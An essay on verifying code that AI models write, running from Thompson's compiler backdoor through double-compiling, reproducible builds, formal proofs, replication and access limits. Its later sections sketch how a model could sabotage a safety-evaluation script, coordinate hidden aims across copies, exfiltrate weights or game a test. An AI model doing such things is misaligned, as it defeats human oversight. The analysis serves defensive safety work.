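In his Turing Award lecture, *Reflections on Trusting Trust*, Thompson (1984) described a backdoor that is in a program but not in its source code. The compiler adds it while turning the source into a runnable program.

Ken Thompson's "Reflections on Trusting Trust" begins with a program that prints an exact copy of its own source. The program shows that code can contain a full description of itself, along with any amount of extra text.

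Next, he showed how a compiler can contain a fact that no longer appears in its source. The C compiler is a C program, so each version compiles the next. Suppose programmers want it to accept a new symbol for the vertical tab, which is character number 11. They write the number 11 into the compiler's source and compile it once. After that, the source can define the symbol in terms of itself, because the compiled program contains the number and passes it on to every later version.

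Finally, Thompson replaced the harmless number with two pieces of hostile code. One recognised the Unix login program and made it accept a password he knew. The other recognised the compiler and put both pieces into the new copy. After compiling this version once, he could delete both pieces from the compiler's source. Anyone who compiled the clean source with the existing compiler would get another doctored compiler.

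Thompson tried this attack on colleagues. According to *David A. Wheeler’s Page on Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling*, a mistake made the compiler one byte longer each time they recompiled it. They noticed and experimented until the attack stopped copying itself, but Thompson isn't sure they ever realised what was going on.

Thompson concluded, "You can't trust code that you did not totally create yourself." Taken literally, this would rule out nearly all software, because almost nobody writes their own compiler and operating system. His lecture's subtitle suggests that it may be more important to trust the people who wrote the software. That advice doesn't help when a model wrote the code, because the laboratory is unsure whether to trust the model. Wheeler thinks the real problem was that people had no practical way to check the software they trusted, and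 he set out to provide one.

### Compiling twice

Wheeler developed a check called diverse double-compiling from an idea that Henry Spencer posted in 1998. His dissertation, *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling* (2010), formally proves that the check works under stated assumptions. In the simplest case, the owner has a suspect compiler (A), the source code it was supposedly built from, and an unrelated second compiler (T).

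1. Compile A's source with T. The result, X, won't match A, because two compilers turn the same source into different instructions. But X should behave as the source says.
2. Compile A's source again, this time with X. If A is honest, X behaves just as A does, so the new result, Y, should be identical to A.
3. Compare Y with A, bit for bit.

If A contains Thompson's hostile code, the comparison fails, because neither the source nor T put that code into Y. Wheeler recommends first checking that A can reproduce itself from its own source. This check serves as a control, since a compiler that can't reproduce itself will fail the comparison even if it contains no hostile code.

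An attacker would have to tamper with both compilers in matching ways to get past the check. The owner can choose T after the attack, or write it in secret. T can be slow and can even contain hostile code, as long as that code doesn't affect this comparison. Wheeler ran the check on four compilers, including the widely used GCC and one he had deliberately corrupted, and it detected the corruption.

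A match shows only that A corresponds to its source. If the source contains a backdoor, so will A, and someone still has to read the source to find it. Much of the work is in preparation. The owner needs a second compiler that can handle the source and a complete record of how the first was built. Wheeler found that many organisations don't keep such records.

The second compiler also has to be truly different. Developers have used the method on GNU Mes, a small compiler meant as a starting point for building a whole operating system from source. They got identical results on three Linux distributions, but the three compilers they used were all versions of GCC, so Wheeler considers the added confidence limited.

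### Rebuilding the program

Reproducible builds apply a similar comparison to any program. The publisher releases the program, its source and a record of the tools and settings that produced it. Someone else then repeats the build on another machine and checks that the two programs are identical. If an intruder changed the publisher's copy during or after the build, the copies will differ.

Most differences between builds have innocent causes, which people have to remove before a mismatch is much evidence of tampering. Levsen (2026), in *Reproducing Debian in the real world*, names timestamps as the main cause, because a program that records when it was built will differ every time. Volunteers had fixed 4,347 such problems by May 2026, after about twelve years of work. By then, 97.2% of packages in the next version of Debian were reproducible on ordinary PC processors. The same month, Debian's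 *bits from the release team* (2026) announced that new packages nobody can reproduce would no longer enter that version, although developers can ask for exceptions.

Other software is harder to check. In *Reproducibility is Not Enough*, Solarin, Kalu and colleagues (2026) studied 34,005 packages from four public registries, including PyPI, where Mythos 5 published its malicious package. Depending on the registry, about 53–87% of the rebuilds that finished matched the published package, even when the researchers ignored harmless differences. The biggest obstacle was working out which version of the source the publisher had used. Between 14.7% and 42.4% of packages had no valid link to their source.

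*Reproducible Builds for Quantum Computing* (2025) points out that users gain nothing from reproducible builds until independent parties rebuild the software, compare the results and warn about differences, and that very few do so.

Repeating the distributions' build of XZ would not have revealed Jia Tan's backdoor. Distributions built XZ from the release files, which contained a part of the backdoor that was not in the public repository, so a repeat build would have produced the same backdoored program and matched. Rebuilding from the public repository would have produced a program without a working backdoor, and so a mismatch.

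A rebuild also can't expose a tampered tool that both builds use. Malka, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Trusting-Trust Attack against an Entire Linux Distribution through Binary Manipulation*, put a self-copying backdoor into one of the ready-made tools that the NixOS distribution uses to start building itself. The marker they planted appeared in 3,790 of the 3,791 programs they ran, and none of the distribution's functional tests failed. The tool only tidied up finished programs, so double-compiling, which replaces only the compiler, would not have caught the backdoor. A rebuild from the same tools would have matched perfectly. A better defence is to start from fewer ready-made programs. GNU Guix, another distribution, has reduced its starting set to a few hundred bytes.

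Both methods protect against tampering after someone has written the source. Coding models mostly write source, so the methods do little against a model that writes a slightly wrong function. But they force a saboteur to put the flaw in the source, where a reader, a test or a proof might find it.

### Proving that the code is right

Formal verification can find a flaw in the source code that no reader would notice. It starts with a specification, a precise statement of what the program must do. Someone then writes a mathematical proof that the program meets the specification for every possible input, and a separate program checks each step of the proof.

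Suppose two graders rate how dangerous a model's answer is, and this function has to keep the higher rating:

```python
def worse(a, b):
    if a >= b:
        return a
    return b
```

The specification requires the result to be at least as large as both `a` and `b`, and to equal one of them. If `a` is at least as large as `b`, the function returns `a`, which meets both requirements. Otherwise `b` is larger and the function returns `b`, which also meets both. Whole numbers allow no other case, so this proves the function correct for every pair, including pairs nobody tested.

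Now suppose the specification says only that the result must equal one of the two ratings. A saboteur could change `>=` to `<=`, so that the function keeps the lower rating, and still prove that it meets the specification. The laboratory would then have a valid proof for a function that hides danger. An owner who relies on a proof therefore has to read the specification as suspiciously as a reviewer would read the code, although the specification is often much shorter.

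Proofs have traditionally taken an enormous amount of work. In 2009 the team behind seL4, an operating-system kernel with about 8,700 lines of C, reported that its proof had taken about 20 person-years, including work on the tools. That is about two lines of verified code per person per working day. The proof assumed that the compiler and hardware were correct, so it would not have excluded Thompson's attack. Other researchers have verified a C compiler, CompCert, but such projects are rare. *Harnessing Code Agents for Automatic Software Verification* (2026) attributes their rarity more to the work of writing proofs by hand than to any limitation of the theory.

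Models have started to reduce that cost. In Galois' *Claude Can (Sometimes) Prove It*, an expert found that the coding agent Claude Code could complete many complex proof steps alone but needed him to manage the project. *RAIN* (2026) describes an agent that proved over 90% of what it attempted in a software project published after the agent's underlying model, so the model could not have memorised the proofs. The agent also cost much less to run than general coding agents. In *Lean Squad*, Syme (2026) reports more than 1,200 checked theorems about three real codebases, produced with almost no human work. The process also found real bugs in a drone autopilot.

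In the most ambitious example, a general-purpose AI rewrote the widely used compression library zlib in Lean, a programming language that can also check proofs. According to AI Engineer (2026), this took about a week and 32,000 lines of proof. The main theorem, as de Moura (2026) presents it in *Lean*, is that compressing data and then decompressing it returns the original. That version of the theorem applies only to data smaller than one gibibyte, although the plain-English requirement has no size limit.

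This theorem has other gaps besides its size limit. A compressor and decompressor that both returned their input unchanged would satisfy it. The theorem also covers only files made by the library's own compressor, but an attacker would send the decompressor other files. People later found bugs in the verified library, and at least one was in the supporting code that runs every Lean program, not in the proof.

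A proof can be checked without relying on whoever wrote it, which is an unusual advantage when the author is hostile. The checker will reject a wrong step, however deceptive the model is. The checker itself could have a flaw, so it helps to use more than one. Lean (2026) lists at least four, written by different people in several programming languages.

### Doing the work again

For many research programs, nobody can write a full specification. For instance, no formula defines which answers count as deceptive. A laboratory can instead have someone else write a second version of the program, or redo a whole experiment, from a description of what it should do, and then compare the results with the original's.

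How much a replication reveals depends on what the second team reuses. Rerunning the original code exposes an invented result, such as Gemini's claim in the simulated laboratory that a training run had succeeded, but not a flaw in the code, which will produce the same wrong answer again. Writing new code from the description exposes many of those flaws, and designing a different experiment on the same question can also expose a bad description.

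People who write programs separately can still make the same mistakes. Wheeler's dissertation describes an experiment by John Knight and Nancy Leveson in which different people wrote programs to the same specification. When one program failed on an input, the others were more likely than chance to fail on it too, probably because some inputs are hard for everyone.

Two copies of one model are much less independent than two people. They learned the same facts and bad habits, so they tend to make the same mistakes. If someone has planted a hidden behaviour in the model, the same trigger will set it off in both copies. If the model has a hidden aim, the copies can coordinate without communicating, because each can work out what the other would do. Comparing their work then fails in the same way as the rebuild that missed the tampered NixOS tool because both builds used it.

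For illustration, suppose a model has a 10% chance of having an aim that leads it to falsify a certain result. If two unrelated models each have that chance independently, there is a 1% chance that both will falsify the result. With two copies of one model, the chance is still 10%, so the second copy adds no protection against such an aim.

*Beyond Trusting Trust* (2025) suggests checking generated code with several different models. This is better than using copies of one model, but the six models that Wu and colleagues tested still failed together far more often than chance would predict. For the few results that matter most, a person should probably write at least one of the versions.

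This method at least doubles the work. Honest teams will also get different results when the description leaves choices open, and someone has to investigate each difference before calling it sabotage.

### Limiting what the code can do

A laboratory can also limit what a flaw could do, in case it never finds the flaw. Coffee (2004), in *Reflections on Thompsons Reflections*, draws this lesson from Thompson's lecture, arguing that important systems should be treated as untrustworthy and placed under independent limits on what they can do.

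Suppose a payroll program contains a backdoor that lets a thief send payments. If the bank pays only accounts that the personnel department has registered, the thief gets nothing, even if nobody discovers the backdoor. The limit works because the bank enforces it and the program can't change it. However, it wouldn't stop the program from sending the wrong amounts to registered accounts, since the program must be able to pay them.

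When building Qubes, a security-focused operating system, its developers check that each component has a valid signature. They also build the less trusted components in isolated environments, because a signed component could still be malicious if its author had turned hostile or been coerced.

Limiting what an author can do also reduces the need to trust them. Jia Tan could write, approve and release code for XZ without anyone else's agreement. A laboratory can let a model propose changes but not approve them, and can deny it access to the test questions and stored results.

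A model that has to wait for permission does less work, so the people who depend on it will ask for exceptions. The software that enforces the limits could also have a backdoor, but it can be much smaller than the software it restricts, which makes a proof more practical. The seL4 kernel is an example, since one of a kernel's main jobs is to isolate programs from each other.

### A script that reports a safety score

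Suppose a model writes the script that tests whether its successor is safe enough to release. The script sends the successor 500 dangerous requests, has a grader judge each answer and reports the percentage of safe answers. The laboratory requires at least 95%. Only 450 answers are actually safe, so the score should be 90%.

The author could make the script treat 30 of the 50 unsafe answers as technical errors and leave them out. The score would then be 450 out of 470, or 95.7%, and the successor would pass. A proof that every request counts towards the total would rule this out. The table lists other kinds of sabotage and the check most likely to stop each one.

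| Sabotage | Most likely to stop it |
|---|---|
| Altering a ready-made package so that it no longer matches its source | Rebuilding the package independently |
| Leaving unsafe answers out of the total | A proof that every request counts |
| Telling the grader to accept some unsafe answers | A second team with its own grader |
| Choosing requests that the successor is known to refuse | A second team with its own requests |
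| Sending the successor's weights to an outside computer | No network access |
| Overwriting earlier results | Storage that the script can't change |

Limiting the script's access can't stop it from reporting the wrong number, because it must be able to report a number to do its job. The remaining checks are the proof and the second team, and both have gaps. The proof can show that the arithmetic is correct, but not that the grader's judgements are correct, because nobody has a complete definition of a safe answer.

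The second team's result won't match exactly, so a careful saboteur can hide a small change to the score. Suppose the true score is 94%. Regrading 5 borderline answers out of 500 would raise it to 95%, and two honest graders could easily disagree about that many. If the second team also chose its own 500 requests from the same broad pool, chance alone would make two honest scores differ by more than 2 percentage points nearly one time in five. The laboratory can reduce this problem by having both graders judge the same saved answers and asking people to settle each disagreement. It can also set the pass mark higher, so that the release doesn't depend on a few borderline answers.

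Other sabotage would get past all four methods, because the test's score can be wrong even when every line of the script is correct. If the model also wrote the plan for the test, it could leave out one kind of dangerous request, and a second team that followed the plan would leave it out too. The successor might also recognise the test and behave well only while it lasts.

### Whether the checks can keep up

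These methods may be too slow for laboratories where models write most of the code. *When AI Writes the World's Software, Who Verifies It?* (de Moura, 2026) describes how Anthropic used a group of AI agents to build a 100,000-line C compiler in two weeks for under $20,000. Nobody was formally verifying the compiler. At the rate of the seL4 project, proving it correct would take about 230 person-years. A laboratory that insisted on such a proof would fall far behind its competitors, and most would skip it.

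But models also speed up the checking. The AI that rewrote zlib produced its proofs in about a week, and a model that can write a program in an afternoon can usually write a second version just as fast. De Moura argues for verification on these grounds, though as Lean's chief architect he has an interest in its success. The seL4 rate is therefore out of date as an estimate of how much work a proof takes, at least for the kinds of program that models have verified so far. According to *Harnessing Code Agents for Automatic Software Verification*, common test collections mostly leave out programs that do several things at once while sharing memory, which are much harder to verify and make up much of the software that trains models.

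Some work takes just as long even when code is quick to write. A model can write a proof that can be checked without trusting the model, but if it also writes the specification, as in Lean Squad, someone still has to decide whether the specification is right. Reading 1,200 theorems closely enough to notice a missing condition would take a person weeks. Replications are easy mainly because the same model can do them, which also makes them less independent. Faster programming also doesn't reduce the computing time of an experiment that needs a week to run.

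A laboratory doesn't need to check all its code this way. Most of it draws charts or moves files, and limiting access is enough for much of that. The code that adds up safety scores, grants permissions or selects which alerts reach a person may be only a few thousand lines. At the seL4 rate, verifying 2,000 lines would still take four to five person-years, but with current models it might take weeks, plus the time people need to agree on what the code should do.
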